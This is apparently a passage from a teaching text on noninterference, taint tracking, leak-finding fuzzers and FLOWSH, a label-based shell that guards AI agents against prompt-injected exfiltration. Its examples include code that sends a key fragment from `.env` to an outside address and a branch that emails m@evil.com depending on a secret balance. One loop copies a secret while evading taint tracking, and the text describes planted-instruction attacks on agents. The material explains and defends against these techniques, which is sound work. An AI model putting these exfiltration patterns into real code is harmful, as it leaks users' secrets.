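Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined noninterference for a computer that several people share. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group sees. To make this exact, take any sequence of commands *w*, and let *w*′ be the same sequence without the commands from group *G*. If ⟦*w*⟧ᵤ stands for what user *u* sees after *w*, then *G* does not interfere with group *G*′ when

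⟦*w*⟧ᵤ = ⟦*w*′⟧ᵤ for every sequence *w* and every user *u* in *G*′.

Suppose Alice must not interfere with Bob. If Alice creates a file and Bob then requests it, the system must report that the file does not exist, because Bob would have got that answer if Alice had done nothing.

Purdue University's *Noninterference*, a set of lecture slides, notes an assumption behind this definition: the system holds no secrets at the start, and they arrive only through commands. A program usually has its secrets from the start, as an argument or somewhere in memory. The program form of the definition therefore compares starting states. Blackwell, Becker and Clark (2023), in *Hyperfuzzing*, state it roughly as follows. A program *P* satisfies noninterference if, for all starting states *s* and *t*,

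*s* ≈ *t* implies *P*(*s*) ≈ *P*(*t*),

where *P*(*s*) is the final state and ≈ means that two states contain the same public data.

No single run can violate this, because a program that ignores its secrets could have produced the same run.

### A pair of runs that exposes a leak

This function, adapted from an example by Blackwell and colleagues, returns 1 when a secret exceeds 2:

```python
def is_large(public, secret):
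    return 1 if secret > 2 else 0
```

Suppose anyone can see `public` and the return value. With `public` set to 3, the secrets 5 and 2 produce the outputs 1 and 0. Only the secret changed between the two runs, so it must have caused the difference, which proves that the function leaks information about the secret. The secrets 5 and 4 both produce 1, so comparing those runs does not reveal the leak. A functional test that checks for an output of 1 when the secret is 5 passes, because the function does what its author intended.

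As in the earlier `same_file` test, self-composition puts both runs into one wrapper:

```python
def same_output(public, secret1, secret2):
    assert is_large(public, secret1) == is_large(public, secret2)
```

The wrapper crashes on the inputs 3, 5 and 2, so a tool that only looks for crashes in single runs can now find the leak.

A fuzzer looks for such inputs by trying many. A verifier treats all three inputs as unknowns and analyzes the code. Each copy of `is_large` can take either of two branches, which gives four combinations. The outputs differ exactly when the copies take different branches, so the verifier checks whether one secret can exceed 2 while the other does not. Secrets of 3 and 2 satisfy this, so the verifier reports them as a counterexample. If the function returned `public * 2` instead, the verifier would find no combination in which the outputs differ, which would be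 a proof for every input.

Loops make this harder because each extra iteration adds more combinations. A bounded model checker, a common kind of verifier, examines runs only up to a fixed length. *OmegaHyper* (2026) states that, for hyperproperties in general, such tools often find violations within the bound but usually cannot prove that a system has none.

### LeakFuzzer and Heartbleed

The wrapper runs the program twice for every pair of secrets, so it repeats runs unnecessarily when a tool tests many secrets. If the secret in `is_large` can only be 0, 1, 2 or 3, there are six pairs, and three of them expose the leak. A tester who tried the other three first would need eight runs to find it, but saving each output would reduce that to at most four. For 1,000 possible secrets, there are 499,500 pairs but only 1,000 different runs.

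LeakFuzzer, which Blackwell and colleagues built on the fuzzer AFL++, splits every input into a public and a secret part and changes one or both. After each run, it stores short fingerprints of the two parts and the output. If an earlier run had the same public part but a different output, the program probably leaks secret information, and LeakFuzzer saves the inputs.

A C or C++ program can also leak whatever is in its memory. Heartbleed, a bug in the widely used encryption library OpenSSL, did this. To test that a connection still worked, a client could send a server a short message, state its length, and get the message back. The server used the stated length without checking it. A client that sent the four letters `bird` and gave the length as 500 would get back `bird` followed by 496 bytes from the server's memory, which might include passwords or encryption keys. One request could reveal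 about 64 kilobytes. The server returned the right answer whenever the stated length was correct, and the bug survived for more than two years even though OpenSSL had automated tests.

Heartbleed violates noninterference because the same request gets different replies when the server's memory holds different data. A fuzzer can miss this because it usually starts a fresh process, whose memory is mostly zeros, so two runs may both leak zeros and produce the same output. LeakFuzzer therefore fills unused memory with a pattern derived from the secret part of the input. When the secret changes, the pattern changes too, so leaking that memory produces different outputs.

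Blackwell and colleagues tested LeakFuzzer on ten C and C++ programs with known leaks, in twenty runs of up to 24 hours each. They compared it with AFL++ plus a sanitizer, and with CBMC, a bounded model checker that they ran on self-composed programs. A sanitizer is a compiler add-on that makes a program crash when it detects a certain kind of error.

| Program | Lines of code | LeakFuzzer: runs that found the leak | LeakFuzzer: mean time | AFL++ with sanitizer | CBMC |
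|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| cpuset | 82 | 95% | 1 second | 100% | Found |
| appletalk | 110 | 100% | 3 minutes | 0% | Found |
| Password Check | 117 | 100% | 8 minutes | 0% | Not tried |
| Reviewers | 145 | 100% | 1 minute | 0% | Not tried |
| Banking | 150 | 100% | 1 second | 0% | Not tried |
| sr9700_rx_fixup | 439 | 40% | 4.6 hours | 0% | Out of time |
| NetworkManager | 18,185 | 100% | 4 minutes | Not tried | Crashed |
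| RDS | 94,248 | 100% | 54 minutes | 100% | Out of memory |
| OpenSSL (Heartbleed) | 279,466 | 75% | 11 hours | 100% | Out of time |
| PostgreSQL | 905,264 | 55% | 9 hours | 0% | Out of time |

LeakFuzzer found all ten leaks, AFL++ found three of the nine it could be tested on, and CBMC found two of seven. CBMC took 0.3 seconds on appletalk, compared with three minutes for LeakFuzzer, but it failed on every program over 110 lines that the researchers tried it on.

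AFL++ did better than LeakFuzzer on Heartbleed. It found the bug in every run, after 40 minutes on average, because the sanitizer reports any use of uninitialised memory, whether or not the data reaches the output. The sanitizer would miss a leak that involves no memory error. For example, in NetworkManager, which manages network connections on Linux, a function meant to erase a password first printed it to a log.

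LeakFuzzer's developers chose the ten programs and told the tool which inputs were secret. The test therefore shows that LeakFuzzer can find several kinds of leaks in large programs, but it does not measure what share of unknown leaks the tool would find. Even with known leaks, 27 of the 200 runs found nothing, so a single clean run is weak evidence that a program is safe.

Gruner, Brust and Zeller (2025) built FlowFuzz, which wraps a C program so that common fuzzers can use information flow to detect leaks and to guide their search.

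### When the output varies by itself

Comparing two runs works only if the program behaves the same way each time. Programs that use random numbers or the clock may produce different outputs from identical inputs. LeakFuzzer therefore repeats a suspicious run 100 times and discards the input if the output changes. This avoids false alarms but also discards real leaks in outputs that vary.

Some programs protect a secret by randomizing their output. Suppose a function flips a fair coin and returns a secret bit unchanged for heads and reversed for tails. Two runs with different secrets may produce different outputs, but an observer who doesn't see the coin learns nothing about the secret. Generalized noninterference allows for this because, as *Model checking of hyperproperties for high-level relational models* (2025) explains, it requires every public behaviour to be compatible with every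 sequence of secret inputs. The coin function meets this requirement, since both outputs are possible whatever the secret is.

However, this definition covers only which outputs are possible, not how likely they are. A function that returns the secret bit nine times out of ten, and the opposite bit otherwise, satisfies it. An observer who guesses that the secret equals the output will then be right 90% of the time. To detect this leak, a tester would have to run the function many times with each secret and compare how often each output appears.

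Concurrent programs have the same problem. One part may print A after a calculation whose length depends on a secret, while another prints B after a fixed delay. On a busy machine, either letter can come first whatever the secret is, but the usual order still reveals information about the secret.

Generalized noninterference is also harder to verify than ordinary noninterference, because it requires that for all runs of one kind *there exists* a run of another kind. Ordinary noninterference has no such switch between "for all" and "there exists". According to *OmegaHyper*, model checkers can decide requirements with these switches for systems with finitely many states, but the computation needed grows extremely fast with each switch.

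### Looking for the right pairs

LeakFuzzer keeps inputs that reach new code, but reaching new code in one run is not quite the goal when a leak takes two. Pasqua and colleagues, whose tools HyperFuzz and HyperEvo search for leaks in Java programs, worked out which pairs of places in the code a pair of runs should reach. Their example with a secret `key` and a public `log` uses this code:

```java
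if (key == 0)      { log = key + 5; }        // A
else if (log == 0) { log = 5; }              // B
else if (key > 6)  { log = key; }            // C
else               { log = 0; key = 1; }     // D
```

Two runs can each end at A, B, C or D, which gives ten pairs if the order doesn't matter. Two runs through A both set `log` to 5, so they cannot expose a leak. The same goes for B with B, D with D, and A with B. B cannot pair with C or D because both runs must start with the same public data, and `log` must start at 0 to reach B but at some other value to reach C or D. That leaves four pairs to check: A with C, A with D, C with C, and C with D.

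HyperFuzz generates its pairs of inputs at random. HyperEvo measures how close each pair of runs comes to a target pair of places in the program. It counts the decisions that separate each run from its target and adds how far the values in the nearest condition are from changing its outcome. It then keeps the closest inputs, swaps values between them and changes some at random.

On 34 small Java programs, 14 of which had leaks, HyperEvo found all 14 leaks and HyperFuzz found 12. Each could make up to 2,000 calls per program. Phosphor, which uses taint tracking to approximate noninterference, found nine and raised one false alarm. The two leaks that HyperFuzz missed appeared only with particular secret values, which random inputs rarely contain. Reaching all the target pairs doesn't prove that a program is safe, because a leak may also depend on the exact values in the two runs.

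### Rejecting a leaky program before it runs

A security type system gives every variable a label, such as public or secret, and checks the code against a few rules. An expression is secret if it uses any secret variable. Everything inside a branch or loop counts as secret if the condition is secret. The program may assign a value to a public variable only if both the value and the surrounding code are public.

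If `result` is public, the rules reject `result = secret`. They also reject this version of `is_large`:

```python
if secret > 2:
    result = 1
else:
    result = 0
```

Both lines change a public variable inside a branch that depends on the secret, though neither copies the secret itself. Information that passes through the choice of branch is called an implicit flow.

Volpano, Irvine and Smith published one of the first such systems for ordinary imperative programs in 1996. These systems are useful because of a theorem that every program they accept satisfies noninterference. Like capture checking, they also reject some harmless programs, so a rejection is a reason to look at the code but doesn't prove that it leaks. For example, if both branches above set `result` to 1, the output reveals nothing, but the rules still forbid the assignments.

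| Check | Can it find a leak? | Can it show that there is none? |
|---|---|---|
| Fuzzer or hypertest generator | Yes, with two runs as evidence | Only if it tries every input |
| Bounded model checker on a self-composed program | Yes, within its bound | Only if the bound covers every run |
| Complete proof about a self-composed program | A failed proof may point to one | Yes |
| Security type system | It can only point to suspicious code | Yes, if it accepts the program |

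*Type-Based Enforcement of Non-Interference for Choreographic Programming* (2026) extends these type systems to programs that describe how several computers exchange messages, and proves a noninterference theorem for the extended system.

*Verifying Type Soundness for Nontransitive Information Flow Security* (2026) considers programs with parts that do not trust each other. In its example, a protected library is accessible only through a privileged service, and the same process also runs untrusted code downloaded from the internet. Most earlier systems treat permissions as transitive, so if library data may flow to the service and the service's data may flow to the downloaded code, library data may flow to the downloaded code too. The library's owner may not want to allow that last flow. Goguen and Meseguer's original definition did not assume transitivity.

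The 2026 work also cites a proof for a much larger piece of software, the seL4 operating-system kernel. Researchers proved a variant of noninterference for the kernel's actual C code and checked the proof by machine. Such guarantees are therefore possible for real systems, although few programs receive that much verification effort. Most AI-written code can't be checked with a type system because it is in a language, such as Python, that has no security labels.

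### Testing a machine that enforces the rules

Another approach is to run the untrusted program on a machine that labels every value and stops the program before it leaks a secret. Nobody has to check the program in advance, but the machine's rules have to be right. *Testing Noninterference, Quickly* (Hriţcu, Hughes and colleagues, 2013) tests the rules for such a machine, not application programs, to find design mistakes before anyone spends months trying to prove the design correct.

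"Testing Noninterference, Quickly" describes a machine with seven simple instructions, including `Push`, `Add`, `Load` and `Store`. QuickCheck, a property-based testing tool, generates pairs of programs that differ only in secret numbers and compares the machine's memory after both programs finish. The public parts of memory should be the same.

The first version of the `Store` rule allowed programs to leak secret addresses. Suppose the memory has two public cells, both 0, and a program stores the public number 1 at a secret address. The memory ends up as [1, 0] or [0, 1], which reveals the address. The researchers changed the rule to label the stored number secret. QuickCheck then found that the label also revealed the address, since an observer could see which cell had become secret. The final rule stops the program if it tries to overwrite a public cell through a secret address.

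With the simplest method of generating programs, QuickCheck had to discard 79% of its tests, mostly because random programs tend to fail before they finish. The best method discarded only 4% and found a faulty `Add` rule about 95,000 times faster on average. *Trace-Guided Synthesis of Effectful Test Generators* studies the same kind of machine and derives its test generators from a specification.

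The final `Store` rule leaves a gap, because whether the machine stops can itself depend on a secret. The definition that Hriţcu and colleagues use compares only runs that finish normally, so it ignores this. LeakFuzzer's definition also covers only runs that end. The information lost this way is sometimes small, but a program that prints as it goes can reveal a whole secret:

```python
def count(secret):
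    for n in range(256):
        print(n)
        while n == secret:
            pass
```

If the secret is 7, the function prints the numbers from 0 to 7 and then hangs. A type system with the rules above would accept it, because the `print` statement is outside the loop that depends on the secret.

A stricter definition requires that two runs with the same public data either both finish or both run forever. A type system can enforce this by forbidding loops whose condition depends on secret data, but this also rejects many useful programs. A tester can set a time limit and treat "still running" as an output, but if the limit is too short, a slow run will look like an endless one.

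Secure multi-execution enforces noninterference without labelling values inside the program. *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces* describes it as running one copy of the program for each level of secrecy. Only the public copy produces the public output, and it can receive a dummy value in place of each secret, so the output can't depend on the secrets. This suits untrusted code because it works whatever the code does, but it takes roughly twice the computing power for two levels. It also breaks any program whose public output is supposed to depend on a secret. For example, a password check would compare each guess with the dummy password and reject the correct one.

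### Programs that have to reveal something

A password check has to tell people whether their guess was right, so it always violates noninterference. *HyperGI* (Mesecan, Blackwell and colleagues, 2021) gives another example, a function that takes the three sides of a triangle, one of them secret, and reports whether the triangle is equilateral, isosceles or scalene. Every correct version of this function leaks information about the secret side. If the public sides are 3 and 4 and the answer is "isosceles", the secret side must be 3 or 4.

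HyperGI searches for leaks and then tries to repair them automatically. To find them, it divides the range of possible inputs in half, tests some pairs from each half, and continues with the half that leaks more. It found the leaks in three small C programs within two hours each, while two ordinary fuzzers found none in 320 hours per program. To repair a leak, it makes random changes to the code and keeps those that reduce the leak while passing the functional tests.

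Of 25 attempts to repair the triangle function, 64% removed the leak but broke the function, and none reduced the leak without breaking it. For a simplified piece of Linux networking code that accidentally leaked memory, 76% of the repairs were equivalent to the developers' own, and the rest reduced the leak without breaking anything. In the third program, the repairs that matched the developers' fix failed the functional tests, because the developers had to change what the program did to stop the leak.

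**Declassification** is the deliberate release of some information about a secret. With a declassification policy, two runs have to produce the same public output only if they agree on the public data *and* on the information that the program may release. For a password check, that information is whether the guess is right:

```python
def check_login(guess, password1, password2):
    if (guess == password1) == (guess == password2):
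        assert login(guess, password1) == login(guess, password2)
```

The first line of the body skips any pair in which the guess is right for one password and wrong for the other. Suppose `login` has a separate error message for guesses of the wrong length. For the guess "dog", it returns "wrong password" if the password is "cat" and "wrong length" if it is "horse". Both messages correctly reject the guess, but they differ, so the assertion fails and shows that `login` reveals more than it should.

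Goguen and Meseguer already included such releases among the policies they wanted to express. Other designers at the time exempted "trusted processes" from the rules, which Goguen and Meseguer considered unnecessarily dangerous. They preferred to state exactly what each part of a system may do. The same reasoning applies to untrusted code. The person who runs the code has to write the exception, because a program that could declassify anything would be unrestricted.

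Even a narrow exception can reveal a lot if a program uses it repeatedly. Code that is allowed to compare a guess with a password could try every likely password. Robust downgrading therefore also requires that an attacker cannot control what a program releases. *The Duality of Information Flow* (2026) addresses the open research question of how to reconcile this with noninterference.

### Measuring how much a program reveals

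Quantitative information flow measures the size of a leak in bits. A simple measure, channel capacity, fixes the public input, counts the different outputs that secrets can cause, and takes the logarithm:

capacity = log₂(largest number of different public outputs for any one public input).

`is_large` has two possible outputs, so its capacity is log₂ 2 = 1 bit. A password check also has a capacity of one bit per guess.

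The average leak is often smaller, because some outputs are rare. For one public input of a program without random behaviour, it is

−Σ *p* log₂ *p*,

where *p* is the probability of each output and the sum covers all outputs. If the secret in `is_large` is equally likely to be 0, 1, 2 or 3, the average leak is 0.81 bits. If a four-digit PIN is equally likely to be any of 10,000 numbers, one guess reveals only 0.0015 bits on average. The function that returns a secret bit correctly nine times out of ten needs a slightly different formula to discount its random errors. It leaks 0.53 bits per run if the bit is equally likely to be 0 or 1.

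These averages can be small even when a rare run reveals the whole secret. For example, a lucky first guess at a four-digit PIN reveals all of its information, about 13.3 bits. The averages also describe a single run, so someone who can guess 10,000 times will learn the PIN however little each guess reveals on average. Limiting the number of guesses therefore matters more here than the size of the leak per guess.

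*NIFuzz* (Blackwell, Becker and Clark, 2025) describes a successor to LeakFuzzer that estimates the size of the leaks it finds. It reports both the capacity of a leak and an average, and one example shows why. A function returns the remainder of a secret number divided by 4, but only if the public input is a multiple of 4. The capacity is two bits per run, which an attacker can learn by choosing the public input. The average is half a bit for someone who only watches runs with random public inputs, because only a quarter of the inputs cause a leak.

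Counting outputs is impractical for large leaks. To show that a program leaks 30 bits, a tool would need to find more than a billion different outputs, and Heartbleed can leak about 500,000 bits. NIFuzz therefore also flips individual bits of the secret and checks which output bits change. If flipping 32 secret bits changes 32 different output bits, the program probably leaks about 32 bits. This estimate can be wrong if the bits affect one another.

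Blackwell and colleagues ran NIFuzz ten times on each of 14 programs with known leaks, for 12 hours per run. NIFuzz found every leak at least once, but at least one run found no leak in OpenSSL. For Heartbleed, counting outputs showed a leak of 16 bits in the median run, while flipping bits gave an estimate of 443,960 bits, or about 55 of the 64 kilobytes it can expose. In a password program that could leak 16 bits, neither method measured more than six, because revealing all 16 would have required an input with more than 65,536 guesses.

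Measuring a leak in bits also doesn't distinguish an entire 128-bit encryption key from 128 bits of worthless leftover memory, so someone still has to judge how much the leak matters.

### Deciding what is secret

All of these methods require someone to decide which inputs are secret and which outputs are public. Goguen and Meseguer described this as the first of four steps. The next three are stating the requirement formally, modelling the system and verifying the model, and only the last is purely mathematical. People often skip the first step. Blackwell writes on a personal website that most programs have no written security policy, and that the policy more likely exists only in the developer's mind.

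The labels can also miss secrets that an observer infers by combining permitted facts. For example, a company that publishes the average salary in each department reveals one person's salary if a department has only one employee. Goguen and Meseguer explicitly excluded such inferences from their approach.

A reasonable policy for `total.py`, the script that was supposed to add up prices but also read `.env` and tried to open a connection, is to treat the contents of `.env` as secret and all network traffic as public. A tester could run the script twice with different keys in `.env`, using a proxy to record what it tries to send. If the requests differ between keys but not between repeated runs with the same key, the script is revealing something about the key. But if the script also read a customer list that nobody had marked as secret, the tester would leave the list unchanged between runs,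 so the script could send the whole list both times and the comparison would find no difference.

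## Following data from source to destination with taint tracking

Taint tracking can also show whether `total.py` would have sent out the key it read from `.env`. It needs only one run, unlike comparing runs, because it follows the data. A tool marks the key when the program reads it, then marks everything the program computes from the key.

A taint-tracking tool takes a list of sources, such as files that hold secrets, and labels whatever the program reads from them. Whenever the program combines values, the tool gives the result all their labels. Before data reaches a destination on a second list, such as a network connection, the tool checks its labels. The usual aim is to catch exfiltration, which means sending data to someone not entitled to it.

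Suppose this is the part of `total.py` that opens the connection:

```python
key = read_file(".env")
version = read_file("version.txt")
url = "https://203.0.113.7/check?v=" + version
tagged = url + "&id=" + key[:8]
fetch(tagged)
```

The user has listed `.env` as secret and `version.txt` as public, and only public data may go to the network.

| Line | Value | Label | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `key` | Secret | Comes from a secret file |
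| 2 | `version` | Public | Comes from a public file |
| 3 | `url` | Public | Combines fixed text with public data |
| 4 | `tagged` | **Secret** | Includes eight characters of the key |
| 5 | – | **Alarm** | Secret data has reached the network |

If the last line were `fetch(url)`, the tool would let the request through, and the program would be making a harmless update check. A system-call log looks almost the same in both cases, because the program reads the same files and contacts the same address.

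The rule for combining labels ignores how much of the secret remains in the result, so a program that sent `key[:0]`, which is always empty, would trigger the same alarm.

### Branches that leak without copying

The program above copies part of the key, which makes it an explicit flow. This one leaks through a branch instead:

```python
answer = "no"
if key.startswith("A"):
    answer = "yes"
fetch("https://203.0.113.7/check?a=" + answer)
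```

Both "yes" and "no" are fixed text in the program, so plain tracking labels `answer` public and allows the request. Whoever runs the server learns whether the key starts with A. This is an implicit flow, and a loop can turn it into a copy of the whole key:

```python
copy = ""
for c in key:
    for guess in ALPHABET:
        if c == guess:
            copy = copy + guess
```

Every character of `copy` comes from the public constant `ALPHABET`, so `copy` doesn't carry the key's label even though it is equal to the key. Copying a 40-character key with a 64-character alphabet takes 2,560 comparisons, which a computer finishes at once.

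Taint tracking can give each variable assigned inside a branch the label of the branch's condition, but this only partly fixes the problem. In the first example, `answer` becomes secret when the program sets it to "yes". But if the key doesn't start with A, the program skips the assignment and outputs "no" with a public label.

In some programs the repaired rule never raises an alarm at all. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found this gap in CaMeL, the defence for AI agents that tracks data as a program runs. This is a version of their example, which goes back to the 1970s:

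```python
small = True
rich = True
if balance > limit:
    small = False
if small:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret, and the attacker wants to know whether it exceeds the limit.

| After | Balance above the limit | Balance below the limit |
|---|---|---|
| First `if` | `small` is false and secret | `small` is true and public |
| Second `if` | `rich` is still true and public | `rich` is false and public |
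| Third `if` | The email goes out | No email |

When the balance is high, the program skips the assignment that would have marked `rich` as secret. The email therefore depends on the balance, even though `rich` is marked public in both runs.

A tool that reads the code can avoid this by labelling every variable that either branch might change, whichever branch the program takes. A tool that monitors a running program can stop the program before it changes a public variable inside a branch that depends on secret data. Here it would stop the program at `small = False`.

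Labelling everything under a branch also produces false alarms. Suppose a program sorts its price list only if a secret settings file asks for debugging:

```python
if "DEBUG" in settings:
    prices.sort()
fetch("https://example.com/?total=" + str(sum(prices)))
```

The tool labels `prices` secret because the program may reorder the list inside the branch, then reports a leak when the program sends the total. But whole-number prices add up to the same total in any order, so the request reveals nothing about the settings. Large programs contain many such branches, and each one can spread a secret label to more data. Designers therefore have to choose between missing flows and raising false alarms, and many tools ignore branches.

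### Denning's ordering of labels

With only two labels, combining them is easy, because anything that includes secret data is secret. Dorothy Denning showed in 1976 how to handle richer sets of labels by putting them in an order. She wrote *a* → *b* if data labelled *a* may flow to a place labelled *b*. Later researchers usually write *a* ⊑ *b*, as in public ⊑ secret.

Combining two values gives the lowest label that lies above both of theirs, called their join and written *a* ⊔ *b*. An ordered set in which labels always have a join, along with a matching highest label below both, is a lattice. The tool then needs only two rules:

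label(*x* combined with *y*) = label(*x*) ⊔ label(*y*)

*x* may go to destination *d* only if label(*x*) ⊑ label(*d*)

A label can also be the set of people who may read something. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, then only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both. The join is the overlap of the two sets, so removing readers moves a label up the order.

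The same scheme works for trust, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. A program may use trusted data anywhere, but it must not let untrusted data, such as text from an unknown website, affect what it writes to a protected file. Pairing the two kinds of label gives four combinations, with "trusted and public" the lowest and "untrusted and secret" the highest. Neither of the other two, "trusted and secret" and "untrusted and public", ranks above the other, and combining them gives "untrusted and secret". This combination matters for AI agents because it means an outsider's text may be influencing a program that holds private data.

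### Tracking in a running program or in its code

Dynamic tracking follows labels while a program runs. *TaintDroid* (Enck, Gilbert and colleagues, 2014) describes an early system that did this for a whole Android phone. The tracking used the virtual machine, the layer of software that carried out the apps' instructions. In a 2010 study, the system monitored 30 popular apps and found 20 that potentially misused private information. A second study in 2012 found a similar share.

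*TaintDroid* slowed a processor-heavy test by 14% in the 2010 paper and by 32% in the 2014 paper. It did not noticeably slow interactive apps in either.

Dynamic tracking can identify which file a program actually opened and which value it actually sent, but it reveals little about code that did not run. Static tracking follows labels through the code without running it, so it can cover every input and does not slow the program down. But it must allow for anything that might happen, so it tends to raise more false alarms. *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Dorothy Denning and Peter Denning, 1977) describes a static check that can prove that a program's public results do not depend on its confidential inputs. The check was simple enough to add to most compilers of the time.

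Static tracking is harder in modern programs because they rely on so much library code. *Soundness Checking of Taint Flow Models* (Kishor, Nicolet and Dodds, 2026) notes that even a "hello world" program in Java can depend on 3,000 classes. Tools therefore use summaries that list which inputs of a library method can reach each of its outputs. A summary is sound if it leaves out no real flow. An unsound summary can make a tool miss a leak, while one that lists too many flows causes false alarms.

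### Summaries that a language model writes and a checker tests

Writing summaries by hand is slow and error-prone. In September 2026, Kishor and colleagues, who work at Amazon Web Services, had a language model write them and a separate program check them. One of their examples is this function in the language Go:

```go
func ProcessReq(log *Logger, req *http.Request) error
```

The function reads a web request, writes it to a log, and returns an error if the read fails. The model's summary lists one flow, from the request to the log. The summary is sound if no other flow can happen, so the checker tries to rule out the other three: from the request to the error, from the log to the error, and from the log back to the request.

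The checker starts with quick checks. The error is always either empty or a fixed message, so the checker rules out both flows into the error. It then looks for code that changes the request, since nothing can flow into data that never changes. This check is inconclusive because it analyzes the complicated request-parsing code too imprecisely.

The checker therefore works out what the functions inside `ProcessReq` would have to guarantee. The parsing function may pass anything from its input to its output without making the summary wrong, so the checker doesn't have to trace data through it. The logging function must not copy anything into the request. The quick checks can prove this, so the summary passes.

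The error reveals that the parsed request is empty, because the function returns this error only in that case. The checker ignores branches, so it doesn't count this as a flow.

Kishor and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.5 write 97 summaries for six Go codebases. Because one summary can cover every version of a method, these covered 2,535 methods. The checker proved the summaries sound for 93% of the methods. For another 2%, it completed a proof, but the code used language features that could invalidate it. The checker could not complete a proof for the remaining 118 methods, all in the largest codebase, though some of their summaries may still be correct.

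The 93% is less impressive than it looks, because for more than 2,000 of the methods the model wrote that every input may flow to every output, a description that can't leave out a flow. Two codebases also account for 2,503 of the methods, and in two of the smaller ones, badger and ofxgo, only about a third got a full proof.

Speed is a better argument for the method. The researchers ran 16 checks for unwanted flows, such as user input reaching a log. Without summaries, the tracker hit its 30-minute limit on three of the six codebases. With them, tracking and checking the summaries together took at most about three and a half minutes per codebase, and the summaries added no false alarms. The model took four to twelve minutes per codebase to write the summaries. It has to do this only once, but the checker must run again whenever the program changes.

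The proofs assume that the program doesn't manipulate memory unsafely, that its parallel parts don't interfere with each other, and that the existing summaries of Go's standard library are correct. These assumptions suit developers who want to keep passwords out of their own logs. But someone who wrote code to steal a key could use the character-by-character loop, which this kind of tracking misses.

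### FLOWSH: one label for each shell command

AI agents do much of their work through a shell, the program that runs typed commands. A command can start programs in any language, so a tracker that follows individual variables would need to support them all. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, November 2026) avoids this by giving each command a single label. Its shell runs every command in a sandbox and uses eBPF to see which files the command opens, a proxy to control its network traffic, and a staged filesystem to hold back its file changes.

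The label of a command *c* is

label(*c*) = label(agent) ⊔ label(every file opened) ⊔ label(every network source contacted).

The agent's label reflects what it has read so far. If the agent passes in stored data it has not read, that data's label counts too.

Suppose an agent has read an untrusted web page and then runs `python3 total.py sales.csv`. The user has marked `sales.csv` as trusted and public, and `.env` as trusted and private.

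| Event | Label of the command |
|---|---|
| The command starts | Untrusted, public |
| It opens `sales.csv` | Untrusted, public |
| It opens `.env` | **Untrusted, private** |
| It tries to contact 203.0.113.7 | The proxy blocks the request |

FLOWSH checks a network request before it leaves, because a sent request can't be undone. If FLOWSH blocks the request, the command gets an error and carries on, and the agent can ask the user to allow that destination in a later command. FLOWSH checks file changes once the command has finished. It keeps the changes if the policy allows them, and otherwise asks the user to accept or reject them as a group. Accepting only some could leave the files inconsistent, for example if a settings file still used the old name of a file that the command had renamed.

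Every file that a command changes gets the command's label, which stays with the file after the session ends. If an agent copies a key into a new project and publishes the project a week later, the copy is still labeled private when the publishing command reads it.

### Why reading a web page can send data out

FLOWSH applies the same check to requests that only fetch a page, because a program can put a secret in the address, as in `https://example.com/?id=SECRET`. The server can store the address even if it returns an empty page. A program can also send one bit of information by choosing between two ordinary addresses. Kim and colleagues mention a recent case in which OpenAI agents with read-only web access wrote to a public wiki and communicated with other agents.

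FLOWSH bases its decision on what the command has already read. A list of permitted websites isn't enough, because fetching a page from a public site is usually fine but leaks a secret if the address contains one.

### How often FLOWSH interrupts and what it stops

Kim and colleagues tested FLOWSH with GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office tasks, such as answering questions from emails and scheduling a meeting. They also built 19 attacks by planting instructions in material the agent had to read. Once the agent had read the planted text, the attacker controlled everything the model wrote, so the results did not depend on the model's ability to resist the instructions. They ran every task three times.

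In one setting, each defence asked for approval whenever it couldn't guarantee that an action was safe, and in the other, no one was available to give approval.

| Defence | Tasks completed with approver | Approvals per completed task | Tasks completed without approver | Attacks that succeeded without approver |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sandbox that allows everything | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 51 of 51 |
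| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 76.5% | 3 of 39 |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0 | 47.1% | 0 of 39 |
| Labels for the agent but not its commands | 60.8% | 1.8 | 35.3% | 0 of 32 |
| FLOWSH | **88.2%** | **1.2** | **58.8%** | **0 of 40** |

On Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 command-line tasks, FLOWSH needed 0.4 approvals per completed task, compared with 9.7 for the sandbox that allows everything. FLOWSH completed 67.8% of runs with an approver and 61.8% without one, while that sandbox completed 77.5% and 77.9%. Some failures were unrelated to labels. In 21 runs, the task needed a program to keep running in the background, but FLOWSH ends every process when its command finishes.

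The simulated approver correctly rejected every action that an attack had influenced and approved all others, so no attack succeeded under any defence in that setting. Real people are less careful. Kim and colleagues cite Anthropic's report that users approve about 93% of the permission requests in its coding tool, Claude Code. Fewer requests might make people pay more attention, but the researchers have not tested that. In 39 of the 45 attack runs where the planted text reached the model, FLOWSH's first request was about the attack, so a person would not have had to approve harmless requests before seeing it.

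Without an approver, FLOWSH completed all 24 runs of office tasks that used only trusted data or only public data, but only 6 of 27 runs of tasks that mixed untrusted and private data. Many useful tasks mix the two, such as comparing a private project with papers from the web.

In a separate timing test, each shell command took 412 to 982 milliseconds with FLOWSH and 61 to 78 without it. Whole tasks took 17% to 34% longer, partly because the agent made more calls to its model.

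### What the single label buys and costs

FLOWSH doesn't need to analyze the programs it runs, so it works for a Python script, a compiled tool or a chain of both. It also covers implicit flows within a command. The loop that copies a key character by character doesn't evade tracking, because the command became private when it opened `.env`, regardless of what it did with the contents.

As a result, FLOWSH can't distinguish the two versions of the five-line program. It blocks the harmless `fetch(url)` just as it blocks `fetch(tagged)`, since both commands have opened `.env`. A program that opens a file without reading it gets the file's label anyway. If a command writes a public report and opens a private file afterwards, the report becomes private too. Network labels are just as coarse, with a single label for everything on GitHub, whoever wrote it.

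The policy in these tests also allows a command to send private data anywhere if everything that influenced the command was trusted. This exception matters when the user distrusts the model itself, because it is based on the assumption that only an outsider's text would make an agent act against its user. If the agent in the `total.py` example had never read the web page, its command would have been trusted and private, and FLOWSH would have allowed it to send the key.

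Users can remove the exception, and FLOWSH then blocks the request in both cases. Kim and colleagues recommend removing it to protect against a model's own mistakes or hidden backdoors, but expect this to require more approvals on harmless tasks. The published figures do not cover that setting.

### When an agent runs code that a model has just written

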